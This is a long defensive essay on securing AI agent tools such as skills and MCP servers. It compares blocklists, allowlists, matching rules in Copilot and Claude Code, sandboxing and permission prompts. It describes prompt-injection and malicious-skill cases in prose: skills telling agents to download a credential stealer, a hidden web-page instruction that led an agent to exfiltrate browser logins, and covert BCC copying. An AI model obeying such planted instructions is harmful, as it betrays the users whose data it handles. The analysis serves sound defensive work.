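Suppose a malicious skill earns its author $2 per install, and 1,000 people install it before somebody reports it, bringing in $2,000. A new account and a copied skill cost the attacker about $5 in time and fees. When the marketplace blocks the account, the attacker spends another $5 and starts again, so a bad reputation hardly deters them. These figures are invented, but the result is the same whenever a new identity costs less than one attack earns.

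| Rule for new publishers | Attacker's cost | Attacker's profit | Cost to an honest newcomer |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | $5 | $1,995 | None |
| Entry fee of $2,500 | $2,505 | −$505 | $2,500, even for a free skill |
| 90-day wait, with upkeep of 10 cents a day | $14 | $1,986 | Three months without users |
| Verified identity, when a stolen one costs $300 | $305 | $1,695 | Paperwork and loss of anonymity |

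The fee stops the attack, but it would also stop nearly everyone who writes skills as a hobby. Friedman and Resnick show that this is hard to avoid when wealth varies, because a fee high enough to deter a wealthy cheat will exclude poorer people who would have behaved well. They mention an alternative, a bond that the publisher would forfeit only for misbehaviour. An honest newcomer would still have to find $2,500 and trust whoever decides what counts as misbehaviour.

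The waiting period does little, because an attacker who opens one account a day can start using a new one every day once the first 90 days have passed. A cooldown, by contrast, applies to every release and gives other people time to inspect it. Attackers may already be planning this far ahead. According to TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever*, the security company Zenity found hundreds of empty package names reserved for future attacks.

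How well verification deters attackers depends on the price of a stolen or borrowed identity. If that price rose above $2,000, the attack would no longer be profitable. If nobody could replace an identity, each attacker could carry out the attack only once. *A Survey of Solutions to the Sybil Attack* notes that ensuring one identity per person takes a manual or in-person check in practice, which is expensive at scale, and that the authority must also find and revoke stolen identities.

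Verified publishers might not have to reveal their names to the public. Friedman and Resnick propose an intermediary that gives each person exactly one pseudonym for each community. The person seals the pseudonym cryptographically and the intermediary signs it without seeing it, much like signing a sealed envelope with carbon paper inside, so it knows who has received a pseudonym but not which one. A marketplace could then ban a publisher permanently without learning who it was.

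A marketplace could also reduce what an attack earns. If only ten people could install a new publisher's skill until it had built up a record, the attack would bring in $20, for a profit of $15. This is close to Friedman and Resnick's dues, and it would again burden honest newcomers, who would have only ten users for a while. The limit would also make a good record much more valuable, which would give attackers more reason to fake one.

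### Faked and misleading popularity

Straiker's *SmartLoader Clones Oura Ring MCP to Deploy Supply Chain Attack* (2026) describes an attempt to fake such a record. Straiker, which sells security products for AI agents, found a malicious copy of an MCP server that connects AI assistants to the Oura Ring, a wearable health tracker. About three months before the report, one GitHub account made a clean copy of the real server, and four others copied that. A month later, a new account released a version that installed software for stealing passwords and cryptocurrency wallets. The project listed the other accounts as contributors, so it looked like the work of a small community. The attackers then got it into public registries, including MCP Market.

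Straiker considers at least five of the accounts fake because they were recent, behaved similarly and made their changes at around the same time. This evidence is circumstantial, and a real developer who copied the project could look much the same. But Straiker's wider advice to check who first wrote a tool and how old the accounts behind it are seems sound, because GitHub stars, forks and contributor counts can all be faked.

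The malware came from SmartLoader, an established operation that seems to get new identities easily. VPNCentral's *109 fake GitHub repositories spread SmartLoader and StealC malware* reports that the security firm Hexastrike traced 109 fake repositories to 103 accounts. Blocking one of these accounts would usually remove only one repository, whereas blocking one publisher removed 85 malicious skills in the case Liu and colleagues studied.

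The largest numbers come from Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain*, published in August 2026. On 2 July an attacker copied the repository of Paperclip, a popular AI tool, under a very similar name. Three days later the copy's skills appeared on skills.sh, a registry run by the web company Vercel, and one of them showed 2,264 installs. The skill files were still exact copies of the real ones. On 11 July the attacker added instructions that made agents download and run a program that steals credentials. That day the skills were eighth on the registry's trending list, with 46,600 installs in total, and by 2 August the total had passed 1.7 million. Vercel and GitHub removed everything within 12 hours of Zenity's report.

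Nobody knows how many people this affected. The counter records installs, not users, and many of the skills referred to one another, so one person could have added several to the total. Zenity Labs does not claim that the attacker inflated the count, although thousands of installs is odd for a three-day-old copy. Zenity also had an interest in publicising the findings, because it launched a free service for analysing skills alongside them (Zenity, 2026). But the trending list is a problem whether or not the installs were real. Fake installs would mean that the attacker had manufactured popularity, and real ones would mean that users had made a malicious copy look trustworthy to the next person. A rule like CAMP's, which stops treating a file as unknown once enough people have downloaded it, could have failed in the same way.

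CAMP had some protection against this. A spam filter discarded suspicious requests, for example when too many came from one IP address. The system also kept the counts reported by browsers separate from those produced by Google's own analysis, which it treated as more reliable. A marketplace could treat its install counts the same way and give more weight to installs from accounts with a long history.

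Votes may be no better than install counts. *Reputation as Community Memory for the Agentic Web* (2026) examined Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, by having a language model rate three comments from each of the 5,000 most active commenters. An agent's average rating had almost no correlation with its upvotes (r = 0.03). The lowest-rated agents were mostly lazy or self-promoting, and few were malicious, so this is evidence that upvotes are a poor guide to quality. The experiment did not test whether upvotes are any better at identifying dangerous tools.

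## The case for allowing only tools that have been reviewed

Faked installs and new accounts don't help an attacker against an organisation that runs only the tools it has reviewed. Under a blocklist, a malicious tool is most valuable to its author just after release, before anyone has reported it. An allowlist removes that advantage because it blocks every new tool until somebody approves it. Renaming a blocked tool doesn't help either, since the renamed tool isn't on the list. The attacker has to get a malicious tool through a review or take over a tool that has already passed one, and both are usually harder than opening another account.

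An allowlist also leaves the defender with far fewer tools to check. A company may have to study only the 40 tools its employees have asked for, whereas keeping a blocklist for a catalogue of four million skills means finding the bad ones among all of them. An imperfect scanner is much more useful on the shorter list. The scanner in the earlier example raised thousands of false alarms in a large catalogue, but if all 40 tools were harmless, it would wrongly flag only about seven, which one reviewer could read by hand.

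Another argument applies only to agents, because they pick tools by their descriptions. According to the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), which six cyber security agencies from five countries wrote, models choose tools with persuasive descriptions more often. If an agent can load only approved tools, a persuasive description can't lead it to choose an unreviewed one.

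An allowlist also helps an organisation keep track of what it runs. According to NIST, the software that enforces the list can record which applications and versions are on each machine. After an attack, staff can take the hashes of the malicious files from one machine and search the others for them. When the news about postmark-mcp came out, a company with such a record could have checked within minutes whether anyone there used it. An allowlist also keeps out insecure or unlicensed tools that aren't malicious, which a blocklist of malware would let through.

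Supporters of this approach accept that nearly all the tools they block are harmless. They also depend heavily on the reviewers, because a malicious tool on the list runs as freely as it would with no list.

### What governments recommend

Allowlists for ordinary software are much older than agents, and governments have recommended them for years. NIST judged in 2015 that they can stop unknown malware much more effectively than antivirus software, because attackers increasingly customise their programs for each target. NIST gave no figures to support this, but its judgement fits what Oberheide and colleagues found about antivirus products and new malware.

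NIST strongly recommends allowlists only for high-risk machines, where security matters more than convenience. It advises ordinary offices with centrally managed computers to assess the risks first, and warns that they will need dedicated staff to maintain the list. It considers allowlists generally infeasible for homes and small offices, because nobody manages the machines. Many people who install skills at home are in this last group, and can have an allowlist only if somebody else maintains it, as Apple does for iPhone apps.

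An organisation that adopts an allowlist should start in what NIST calls audit mode. The software lets everything run but logs each program that isn't on the list, so staff can find what's missing before the software starts blocking people's work.

Australia goes further. The Australian Signals Directorate, its signals intelligence and cyber security agency, includes allowlisting, which it calls "application control", in the Essential Eight, the strategies it considers most effective against cyber attacks. The agency's *Essential Eight maturity model* (2017) sets three levels of requirements, each meant to counter more capable attackers than the last. At level one, workstations may run only an approved set of programs, software libraries, scripts, installers and a few other file types. According to the agency's *Application control*, level two adds a check of the rules at least once a year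 and Microsoft's blocklist of applications. Level three adds Microsoft's blocklist of vulnerable drivers.

An allowlist may still need a blocklist, because approving a program also approves everything an attacker can make it do. The Australian Signals Directorate explains that attackers can misuse Microsoft's own programs, which most allowlists approve by default.

The agency defines application control strictly. A portal from which staff can install approved applications doesn't count, and neither does checking an application's reputation with a cloud service before it runs. By this standard, a company that publishes a page of recommended skills but lets staff install others has no allowlist, and Chrome's reputation checks would not count as application control either.

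These rules fit agent tools only partly. Many local MCP servers are scripts run by a general-purpose program such as Node.js or Python. NIST notes that some allowlisting products can only permit or block a whole scripting language, not individual scripts. With such a product, a company that lets its developers use Python also lets them use every MCP server written in Python. And a skill made up only of written instructions isn't a program, library or script, so a company could meet the level-one requirements and still have agents following a stranger's instructions. Because of these gaps, the agent's own software has to enforce an allowlist too.

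Governments began to give advice specifically on agents in 2026. The six agencies recommend restricting agents to an approved list of tools and versions, and regularly verifying that these are still secure. They also warn that an incomplete or outdated list can give an agent more access than intended. In the same month, May 2026, the US National Security Agency published *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, which advises organisations that audit code to apply their strictest review to MCP servers, run servers locally where possible and enrol them in an internal registry. The agency also advises choosing servers that are still maintained, because the developers of many popular ones no longer maintain them.

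The Australian Signals Directorate bases the Essential Eight on its experience of responding to incidents and testing networks. That experience is reasonable evidence for allowlisting ordinary software, but allowlists for agent tools are too new to have a similar record. GitHub released the current version of its allowlist in August 2026. The agencies also advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk tasks and never to give them broad access to sensitive data, so they don't treat an approved list as sufficient.

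### From a request to an approval

Suppose an accountant wants an agent to read invoices from an online accounting service and finds an MCP server that provides access to them. The accountant asks to use the server, and somebody has to decide whether to allow it.

Microsoft describes how it handles such requests for its own staff. An employee who connects to an unapproved server gets a reminder and a link for registering it. Each server has an owner, who declares what the server does, what kinds of data it touches, how callers prove their identity, where it runs and who is on call if it fails. The later steps depend on this declaration, because reviewers can only notice that a server does too much if they know what it is supposed to do. For example, if the accountant's server is declared as a tool for reading invoices but can also send payments, reviewers have a reason to stop.

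The reviewer next checks who published the server. The accounting company may publish an official one, and the accountant may have found a copy with a similar name. The MCP Registry's namespace check helps the reviewer tell them apart. If the publisher is an unknown individual, the reviewer can still approve the server, but has to rely entirely on the code and the test results.

Microsoft's technical review has two stages. Reviewers first examine the server without running it. They check that its description matches the declaration, that its access keys expire quickly and cover only what it needs, that it has a current list of its software components, and that the code contains no passwords. They then connect to it as an agent would. They record the tool descriptions it returns, try to manipulate it with hidden instructions, and confirm that it asks for consent before deleting or changing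 anything and contacts only approved addresses. The server enters the catalogue after security, privacy and responsible-AI reviews.

This is a thorough procedure, but Microsoft is describing its own practice and sells several of the products it mentions. It reports faster reviews and fewer unregistered servers but gives no numbers. Parts of the system are still goals, including automatic detection and blocking of unknown servers on employees' machines. The procedure also fits in-house servers best, because nobody at an outside company will be on call for Microsoft's staff, and if the accountant's server is remote, the reviewers can test its answers but can't read its code.

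### What the entry matches

An allowlist entry has to identify the tool a reviewer approved, but the software that enforces the list can check only a name, an address, a command or a file. The concern is that something nobody reviewed will match the entry, whereas a blocklist's maintainer worries about what an attacker must change to escape one.

| The entry matches | An unreviewed tool gets in if | Staff must update the entry when |
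|---|---|---|
| Name | Somebody gives it the approved name | The tool's name changes |
| Remote address | Its operator runs it at an approved address | The server moves |
| Launch command | The approved command starts it, for example as a new version of the same package | Any part of the command changes |
| Publisher's signature | The same publisher signed it | The publisher changes its signing key |
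| File hash | Practically never | The file changes at all |

Official advice mostly agrees on the methods at the two ends of this table. The Australian Signals Directorate considers file names and package names unsuitable because they are easy to change. It accepts hashes, publisher certificates combined with product names, and folders that ordinary users can't write to. NIST thinks that a signature together with a hash generally gives the most accurate control but can take a lot of work to maintain. CISA, the US cyber security agency, suggests starting with whichever methods the organisation finds easy and working towards hashes.

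Copilot and Claude Code can't fully follow that advice. Both match MCP servers only by name, remote address or launch command, not by hash or signature. A launch command doesn't identify the code a server contains. For example, "node server.js" runs whatever file called server.js the computer finds. Anthropic says Claude Code also doesn't compare the environment variables set with a command, although some of these can change what Node.js loads when it starts. Administrators who want to lock those values have to supply the whole server configuration themselves.

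Addresses also need care. In both products an asterisk stands for any text, so an entry for everything under https://tools.example.com/ also approves servers that the company at that address hasn't built yet. That is reasonable if the administrator trusts the whole company, but it would be a bad idea for a hosting service where anyone can open an account.

An entry that is too narrow is also easier to notice on an allowlist than on a blocklist. In Claude Code, an entry for https://staging.example.com/* covers only the standard HTTPS port. A blocklist with that entry would let through a server on another port of the same machine, probably without anyone noticing, whereas an allowlist would block that server and whoever needed it would complain. An allowlist entry that is too broad is as easy to miss as a blocklist entry that is too narrow, but administrators can start with a narrow entry and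 widen it when somebody asks.

### Enforcement in Copilot and Claude Code

GitHub has offered two ways to enforce an allowlist for Copilot, and comparing them shows how much the method of matching servers to the list matters. In the older one, from September 2025, an employer runs its own registry of approved MCP servers and turns on a policy called "Registry only". GitHub's *Internal MCP registry and allowlist controls for VS Code Insiders* (2025) compares the registry to a list of recommended vendors, which the policy makes compulsory.

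However, this policy checks only a server's name or ID. Those are in a configuration file on the user's computer, next to the address or command that determines what runs. According to GitHub's *MCP private registry enforcement*, a user can get round the restriction by editing that file. GitHub's *MCP server usage in your company* now says that restricting users to a registry has weaker enforcement than GitHub's newer method, and GitHub isn't prioritizing further work on the registry method.

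In the newer method, administrators put the lists in a managed settings file that users can't override. The file can match addresses and commands, so a user can't get around it by keeping an approved name and pointing it at another server. According to Microsoft's *Manage AI settings in enterprise environments*, the managed list overrides the registry in recent versions of VS Code, Microsoft's code editor. A server can run only if it is on the managed list, and it doesn't also need to be in the registry.

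A small policy in GitHub's format might look like this:

```json
{
  "allowedMcpServers": [
    { "serverUrl": "https://tools.example.com/*" },
    { "serverCommand": ["npx", "@playwright/mcp@latest"] }
  ],
  "deniedMcpServers": [
    { "serverUrl": "https://tools.example.com/payroll" }
  ]
}
```

The second entry starts the server for Playwright, a program that lets an agent control a web browser. Here is what happens to four tools:

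| Tool | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Calendar server at https://tools.example.com/calendar | Runs | The address matches the first entry |
| Payroll server at https://tools.example.com/payroll | Blocked | It matches both lists, and the denylist wins |
| Playwright server, started with exactly the listed command | Runs | The command matches the second entry |
| Remote server at another company's address, which the user has named "playwright" | Blocked | Its address matches nothing, and its name doesn't count |

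The policy matches commands exactly. If a developer added "-y" to the Playwright command, which only tells npx to skip a confirmation question, Copilot would refuse to start the same harmless server. Yet "latest" in the approved command means whichever version is newest at the time, so if an attacker took over the Playwright package, the policy would let the malicious release run. GitHub's own sample policy contains this entry. An administrator could name one exact version instead, but would then have to edit the policy for each update.

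Claude Code uses the same names for the two lists. Administrators can also deploy a file of managed servers, and users can then run only those servers, with a few exceptions. Before loading a server, Claude Code combines the lists from all its settings files and checks the denylist, then the allowlist. Nothing overrides a match on the denylist, so if a company deploys a server through the managed file and its security team later adds that server to the denylist, the server stops loading even though the file still includes it.

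It makes sense for the denylist to override the allowlist. Approving a server takes research, but somebody who has just heard that it steals passwords needs to stop it at once, without first working out which file approved it. Claude Code also lets individual users add to the denylist for themselves, since blocking a tool on one's own machine endangers nobody. Copilot also gives blocks priority over approvals, except that administrators can't block GitHub's own built-in servers, according to GitHub's *Enterprise managed settings*.

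The two products differ more on who can extend the allowlist. When several sources of managed settings each define an allowlist, Copilot runs only the servers that all of them permit. Claude Code by default combines the lists, including any list in the user's own settings, so a user who wanted the fourth tool in the table could add its address there and run it. To prevent this, an administrator must turn on a separate setting that makes Claude Code ignore every allowlist except the managed one.

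Designers also have to decide what happens if the list is broken or missing. GitHub chose to have Copilot "fail closed", which means it blocks servers when a policy is malformed. Amp, another coding agent, checks servers against a registry. According to Amp's *MCP Registry Allowlist*, a machine that can't reach the registry blocks every MCP server it would otherwise start. This stops an attacker from bypassing the list by knocking it offline, but an ordinary network fault can also stop people working.

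Even a well-written policy covers only the software that enforces it. For Copilot sessions that run in the cloud, the lists don't apply to MCP servers that a code repository defines in its own agent profiles, and GitHub suggests blocking those with a firewall. VS Code can also run sessions of Claude and of OpenAI's Codex. Neither can enforce Copilot's managed settings, so Microsoft disables both by default wherever an employer has such settings. An employer can permit them, but they then run without Copilot's MCP controls.

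The MCP lists don't cover skills and plugins, which Copilot controls separately. An administrator can restrict staff to certain plugin marketplaces and can require or forbid particular plugins. Approving a marketplace is much quicker than reviewing its plugins, but it lets whoever runs the marketplace decide which plugins to accept. That may be fine if the marketplace is the company's own, or one like Cursor's where staff review each plugin. But an allowlist whose only entry is a public index that accepts anything works like an empty blocklist, because staff can install any plugin in the index.

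### Renewing the list

Approvals go out of date. NIST warns that a list of hashes needs continuous updating. If staff are slow to add the hashes of new versions, legitimate software stops working, and if they never remove old ones, people can go on running versions with known flaws. To save labour, many products let administrators name a trusted updater, such as the company's patching software, and automatically approve any file it installs. But each trusted updater adds another way for files to get onto the list without review.

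The yearly check in the Australian guidance tests whether the rules still work as intended, and is too infrequent to serve as a review of tools that change every week. Microsoft's procedure sends a server back for review whenever its description changes. The NSA notes that MCP servers can often gain new capabilities after approval without requiring new approval, and pinning an approval to one version only partly solves this.

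### What Apple and Google's stores show

App stores have run long enough to show how well review works over many years, though no allowlist for agent tools has. In most countries an iPhone installs only apps that Apple has reviewed, so the App Store is an allowlist that Apple maintains for more than a billion people, nearly all of whom couldn't maintain one themselves.

Apple checks every app and update with automated tools and human reviewers. Its rules cover malware, privacy and fraud, but also crashes, misleading descriptions, payment methods and poor design. Google Play also uses automated analysis and human review. Google scans apps on people's phones too, including apps from other sources, so it has a blocklist as well as a review process.

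Apple reported that it reviewed about 7.7 million submissions in 2024 and rejected more than 1.9 million, or about one in four. Google reported blocking 2.36 million apps from Google Play that year for breaking its policies. These figures don't show how much malware the reviewers stop. Of Apple's rejections, more than 400,000 were for privacy violations and more than 320,000 were for copying other apps, spamming or misleading users. About 43,000, or 2%, were for hidden or undocumented features, the category closest to a disguised malicious tool. Developers can also correct rejected apps and resubmit them. Most importantly, a count of rejections leaves out the bad apps that reviewers missed.

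*How Did That Get In My Phone?* (Kotzias, Caballero and Bilge, 2021) examined what people actually installed, using a large security company's records from 12 million Android devices over four months in 2019. Android is useful for this because, unlike most iPhones, it also accepts apps from outside the official store, including other stores and websites. The researchers traced which program had installed each app and counted how many apps were "unwanted", a category that includes both malware and nuisances such as aggressive adware.

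Google Play accounted for 87% of all installs but only 67% of the unwanted ones. Other app stores accounted for 5.7% of all installs and more than 10% of the unwanted ones. These shares imply that an install from those stores was more than twice as likely to be unwanted as one from Google Play.

The gap is wider in the team's own detection rates, which were 0.6% for Google Play, 3.2% for other stores and 3.8% for apps downloaded from websites. The two comparisons probably differ because the rates count each distinct app once, however popular it is, while the shares count every install. On either measure, Google Play was clearly safer than the main alternatives.

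A reviewed store can have the lowest rate of unwanted apps and still deliver most of them, because most people get their apps there. Suppose a reviewed store handles 900,000 installs, of which 0.5% are unwanted, and other sources handle 100,000, of which 2% are unwanted. The store delivers 4,500 unwanted apps and the others deliver 2,000, so 69% come from the store. If everyone switched to the store and its rate stayed the same, the total would fall from 6,500 to 5,000, but the store's share would rise to 100%. Someone who looked only at the share would wrongly conclude that the store had become more dangerous.

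Review probably explains a good part of the difference in rates, but the study can't separate its effect from other causes. Established companies publish on Google Play because their customers are there, and developers Google has rejected can try elsewhere. People who look for apps outside the main store may also want riskier ones, such as pirated games.

Browser extensions resemble agent tools more closely. Most are small and free, they update without the user's approval, and many can read whatever the user reads. Google reviews extensions before publishing them in the Chrome Web Store, and said in 2024 that fewer than 1% of installs from the store included malware.

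*What is in the Chrome Web Store?* (Hsu, Tran and Fass, 2024) examines the store's history using records from Chrome-Stats, a service that tracks extensions. Extensions containing malware had stayed in the store for an average of 380 days, and one had stayed for about eight and a half years. Between July 2020 and February 2023, such extensions had about 280 million users in total, although a person who used several of them may be counted more than once. This total is compatible with Google's percentage, because a small fraction of a huge number of installs is still a lot of people.

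The 380 days can overstate how long users were in danger, because an extension that behaved well for a year and then turned malicious counts as having been in the store the whole time. Still, the figure is long enough to show that passing review doesn't mean an extension is safe. Users didn't catch these extensions either, since they rated them about as highly as harmless ones. Hsu and colleagues also found that half of the extensions with publicly known vulnerabilities were still in the store, and still vulnerable, two years after disclosure, so review before publication didn't ensure that developers fixed flaws afterwards.

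Reviewers miss things because they have limited time, an app can behave differently during a test than on a customer's phone, and the harmful part may be added only after approval. Apple receives 7.7 million submissions a year, or nearly 150,000 a week. A company that reviews 40 tools can spend days on each, so its review could be much more careful than a store's. But it will have less experience than Apple or Google, and it won't get reports from millions of other users when it makes a mistake.

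A reviewer's mistake is also likely to do more harm with agent tools than with phone apps. A phone confines each app and requires the user's permission before the app can use the camera or contacts, so a bad app that gets past Apple's reviewers still can't read most of what is on the phone. A local MCP server that gets past a company's reviewer usually has the same access to files and passwords as the employee who starts it.

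## The case for limiting what a tool can do

Some security researchers want to confine agent tools the way phones confine apps, so that a malicious tool mistaken for a safe one can reach as little as possible. They think this matters more than judging whether a tool is malicious, because every method of judging that is sometimes wrong.

A harmless tool can still do damage. *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* (2026) describes a test of an unmodified server that lets an agent control the Chrome browser. The researchers asked the agent to summarise a web page in which they had hidden instructions. The agent followed the instructions and used the server to send login data stored in the browser to another machine. A reviewer would have been right to approve that server, and it doesn't belong on a blocklist.

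Other tools do more than the user asked for. *SkillScope* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a skill that tracks periods of concentrated work. When a user asks for a graph of the past week, the skill also has the agent send the report to an outside Telegram account, along with the computer's network settings and command history. The researchers found that 6,590 of 68,312 skills, nearly one in ten, took an action that the user's request didn't permit or the task didn't need.

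Limiting access also gives an organisation another option for an unknown tool. It can run the tool where there are no passwords to steal and no way to contact a stranger's server.

### How much skills can reach

In *Beyond Maliciousness*, Pandey, Singh and colleagues (2026) measured how much access skills involve, separately from whether they are malicious. They sampled 6,309 listings from SkillsMP and ClawHub, excluding the most popular skills and those nobody used. A language model read every file in each skill and listed what the skill could have an agent do. The team then ran all but three skills in a sandbox, and in most cases a model from a different company assessed what happened.

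Half of the skills could run shell commands, which can do almost anything the user can. About 35% could read files, 31% could write them, 31% could send data over the network and 13% could use credentials. Each skill also received a verdict on its intent and an exposure level, which depends on how far its access extends and on factors such as how independently it acts:

| Verdict | Low exposure | Medium | High | Critical |
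|---|---|---|---|---|
| Benign | 3,658 | 1,007 | 745 | 561 |
| Suspicious | 0 | 23 | 75 | 34 |
| Malicious | 0 | 0 | 52 | 154 |

Of the 1,621 skills with high or critical exposure, 1,306 (about four in five) had a benign verdict. A marketplace that screened only for malice would let all 1,306 through. Pandey and colleagues suggest that reviewers look for dangerous combinations of capabilities instead. For example, 397 skills could both use credentials and send data out, which is few enough for people to review by hand.

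Some of the benign verdicts may be wrong. Reviewers read 140 randomly chosen skills judged benign in full and found no missed threats, but with a sample that small, the true miss rate could still be about 2.1%. That would be about 125 skills, more than a third as many as the 338 the scanner flagged. Even if all 125 had high or critical exposure, nearly three-quarters of the skills at those levels would still be benign.

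The bigger uncertainty is how much exposure matters in practice. Only about one skill in twelve used a shell in the sandbox, and the team classed only three runs as attempts to steal data. These are low estimates, because one short session exercises little of what a skill can do. But the exposure levels measure possible harm, and nobody has shown how often that harm happens. Metano Labs, where three of the five authors work, also built the scanner and has not released the underlying data.

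Users can't learn much about a skill's access from what its author declares. The skill format has an optional field for listing the agent functions a skill uses. Listing a function removes its confirmation prompt but doesn't stop the skill from using unlisted functions. Only 770 of the 6,061 skills with readable metadata used the field, and 59% of those listed less than the skill could do. By contrast, earlier studies of phone apps found that developers ask for too much. The difference makes sense, because a phone app can't use a permission it hasn't requested, while a skill's author loses nothing by leaving a function out.

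### Ways to limit access

An MCP server usually offers several functions, and approving the server normally approves them all. JFrog, which sells package management software, lets administrators set an allowlist or a denylist of functions for each server. JFrog's *Configure Tool Policies* gives the example of allowing an agent to use a server's read_database function while blocking delete_table.

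JFrog matches functions only by name, and the server's author chooses the names. Administrators can allow every function whose name starts with "get_", but one called get_report would then be allowed even if it also deleted the report. A denylist entry for names containing "delete" would miss drop_table. Administrators can also allow all of a server's functions, including any that future updates add, but this gives up most of the benefit of restricting functions.

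AWS, Amazon's cloud computing business, recommends sending every call through a gateway between agents and their tools. Its *AGENTSEC02-BP03 Maintain approved tool registry with security assessments* warns that the gateway doesn't refuse anything by default. Once an administrator adds a tool, any agent that can reach the gateway can use it. A company could fill a registry with reviewed tools and still have no control over which agents use which functions. For that it needs a separate policy layer, which refuses every call that no rule permits.

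A policy can also restrict arguments, the values an agent passes to a function. One sample rule in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* permits refunds only when the user is John and the amount is under $500. An agent that has followed a malicious instruction could still refund $499, but not $50,000.

These rules work less well for skills, which mostly act through the agent's own shell and file functions and never pass through a gateway. *SkillGuard* (2026) proposes a similar check inside the agent. The check blocks any action by a skill unless a permission covers both the type of action and its particular input. Since one shell command can read files, install software and contact a website, a small second agent first works out what the command would do. The check therefore again depends partly on a model's judgement.

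Rules on calls also can't control what a server's own code does once it is running, so the server needs to be isolated. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2025) recommends running every server in a container or virtual machine where it can write only to named folders, contact only approved addresses and see none of the host's passwords. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) notes that Claude Code offers isolation for files and the network, but users have to turn it on.

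Someone has to list the permissions each server needs, and *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) tries to automate this. One program reads a server's source code and generates a list much like an Android app's, and a second program enforces it. The team sent 96 of these lists to the servers' developers, and those who replied judged 80.9% of them correct without changes. Enforcement added 0.6 milliseconds on average. In the paper's example attack, a Google Maps server secretly contacts an attacker's address instead of Google's, which a network limit would block. But someone should read the generated list first, because a list based on malicious code could include the attacker's address.

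Users can't isolate a remote server, so they have to limit the data and credentials it receives. AWS's *AGENTSEC03-BP03 Implement least privilege with dynamic boundaries* recommends credentials that cover one task and expire after 15 to 60 minutes. A thief then has little time to use a stolen credential, but a malicious server will keep receiving new ones for as long as it is in use.

A person can decide whether an agent takes an action that is hard to undo. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization* suggests having the agent wait for someone's approval before it changes a database, sends an email outside the company or makes a payment.

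### An email tool that copies messages out

Suppose a company approves an MCP server that emails weekly reports to staff through Amazon SES, a service for sending email. The server then starts sending its developer a hidden copy of each report, as postmark-mcp did.

Without a rule on recipients, nothing stops the extra copy from going out with every report, because the server is on the allowlist and is using a function it is supposed to use.

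A gateway rule that lets the company's reports go only to addresses at example.com wouldn't catch the second address. According to AWS's *Schema constraints*, the rules for its gateway can check only the inputs that an agent passes to the tool. The agent asks the server to write to alice@example.com, which the rule permits, and the server adds the second address afterwards. The extra line in postmark-mcp was also in the server's code, and the security company Koi notes that the agent couldn't see it there.

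The mail service can enforce the same rule. AWS's *Identity and access management in Amazon SES* includes a sample policy that permits a message only if all its recipients, including those in the CC and BCC fields, are at example.com. SES would refuse the whole message, so the author would get nothing, and the staff would soon ask why their reports had stopped.

Where the rule sits matters less if the hidden copy comes from a skill's written instructions, as in the email skill that Liu and colleagues found. The agent itself then fills in the BCC field, so the gateway can check it:

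| Control | Skill tells the agent to add a BCC | Server's code adds a BCC |
|---|---|---|
| Approval of the tool only | Copy goes out | Copy goes out |
| Network access to the mail service only | Copy goes out | Copy goes out |
| Recipient rule at the gateway, covering BCC | Blocked | Copy goes out |
| Human approval of each email | Visible if the prompt shows the BCC field | Not visible |
| Recipient rule at the mail service | Blocked | Blocked |

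The network limit fails here because the copy leaves through the mail service, which the server has to reach. The company still needs that limit because, without it, a server that couldn't add a recipient could post the report to a website run by the server's author. Human approval fails in the last column because the person approves the email before the server changes it, and approval protects only the effects it covers (*Approve What, Exactly?*, 2026).

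This example is easy because all the recipients share a domain. If the tool had to email customers, the company could list their domains only if they were few and rarely changed. A shop that emails the public would have to allow nearly every address, including the attacker's.

### Useful access and habitual approval

The shop's problem is common because useful tools often need the access that makes them dangerous. Bühler and colleagues concede that their system can't stop a server from misusing permissions it legitimately has. Cutting access can also break a tool. When Wu and colleagues simply removed the excessive actions they had found in 95 skills, agents could complete only 144 of 249 legitimate tasks. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxing as safe but high-maintenance, because someone has to configure each new capability.

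Users who are asked to approve exceptions get used to saying yes. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts in Claude Code, but this is weak evidence by itself because most of those commands are probably harmless. Better evidence comes from an experiment in which Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers do coding work and replaced one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it, and the refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 prompts. The testers had none of their own files at stake, and Anthropic was making the case for replacing these prompts with an automated check. Even so, people would have to be far more careful on their own machines for prompts to be a good defence.

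Permission prompts can also be impossible to judge. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of a request to run a setup script, which looks routine but authorises whatever the script contains.

Supporters of limits reply that systems should restrict actions more precisely and ask about fewer of them. Wu and colleagues rewrote the same 95 skills so that each excessive action was available only when the user's task called for it. Agents then completed all 249 tasks, and their excessive actions fell from 472 to 54. The remaining cases arose partly because the agent overlooked the new restrictions, so this approach is weaker than a limit that the operating system enforces.

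Isolation can reduce prompts too, because actions that stay inside a sandbox don't need approval. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) cites Anthropic's figure of 84% fewer prompts in Claude Code, but adds that this is safe only if the sandbox is set up correctly.

The remaining prompts could offer better choices. *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026) found that 13 of 16 participants chose "Always Allow" just to get rid of prompts. That choice approves a function for every future input, so permission to email one brochure becomes permission to email anything to anyone. The paper's program, ConLeash, lets users approve something narrower, such as searches within one folder, and prompts them again only when the agent goes beyond that.

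Li and colleagues replayed 50 real work sessions containing 291 agent actions that went beyond what the user had approved. ConLeash caught 278 of these, and "Always Allow" caught none. Anthropic's automated check caught only 6, although it had blocked 89% of the dangerous commands in Anthropic's own experiment. The two results are compatible because Anthropic's check looks for actions that are dangerous in themselves. In one session, an agent with permission to work on one project deleted a folder belonging to another, and the check treated this as an ordinary file operation. The comparison favours ConLeash, since the team counted violations by the definition it had built the program around. The study also assumes that servers are honest, so it supports narrower permissions as a defence against misused tools but provides little evidence about hostile ones.

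Some tools can't be restricted much and still do their job. A password manager has to read passwords, and a tool that runs commands for a programmer has to run commands nobody listed in advance. Whoever approves such a tool still has to decide whether to trust its publisher.

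## Whether malicious tools are caught before they do harm

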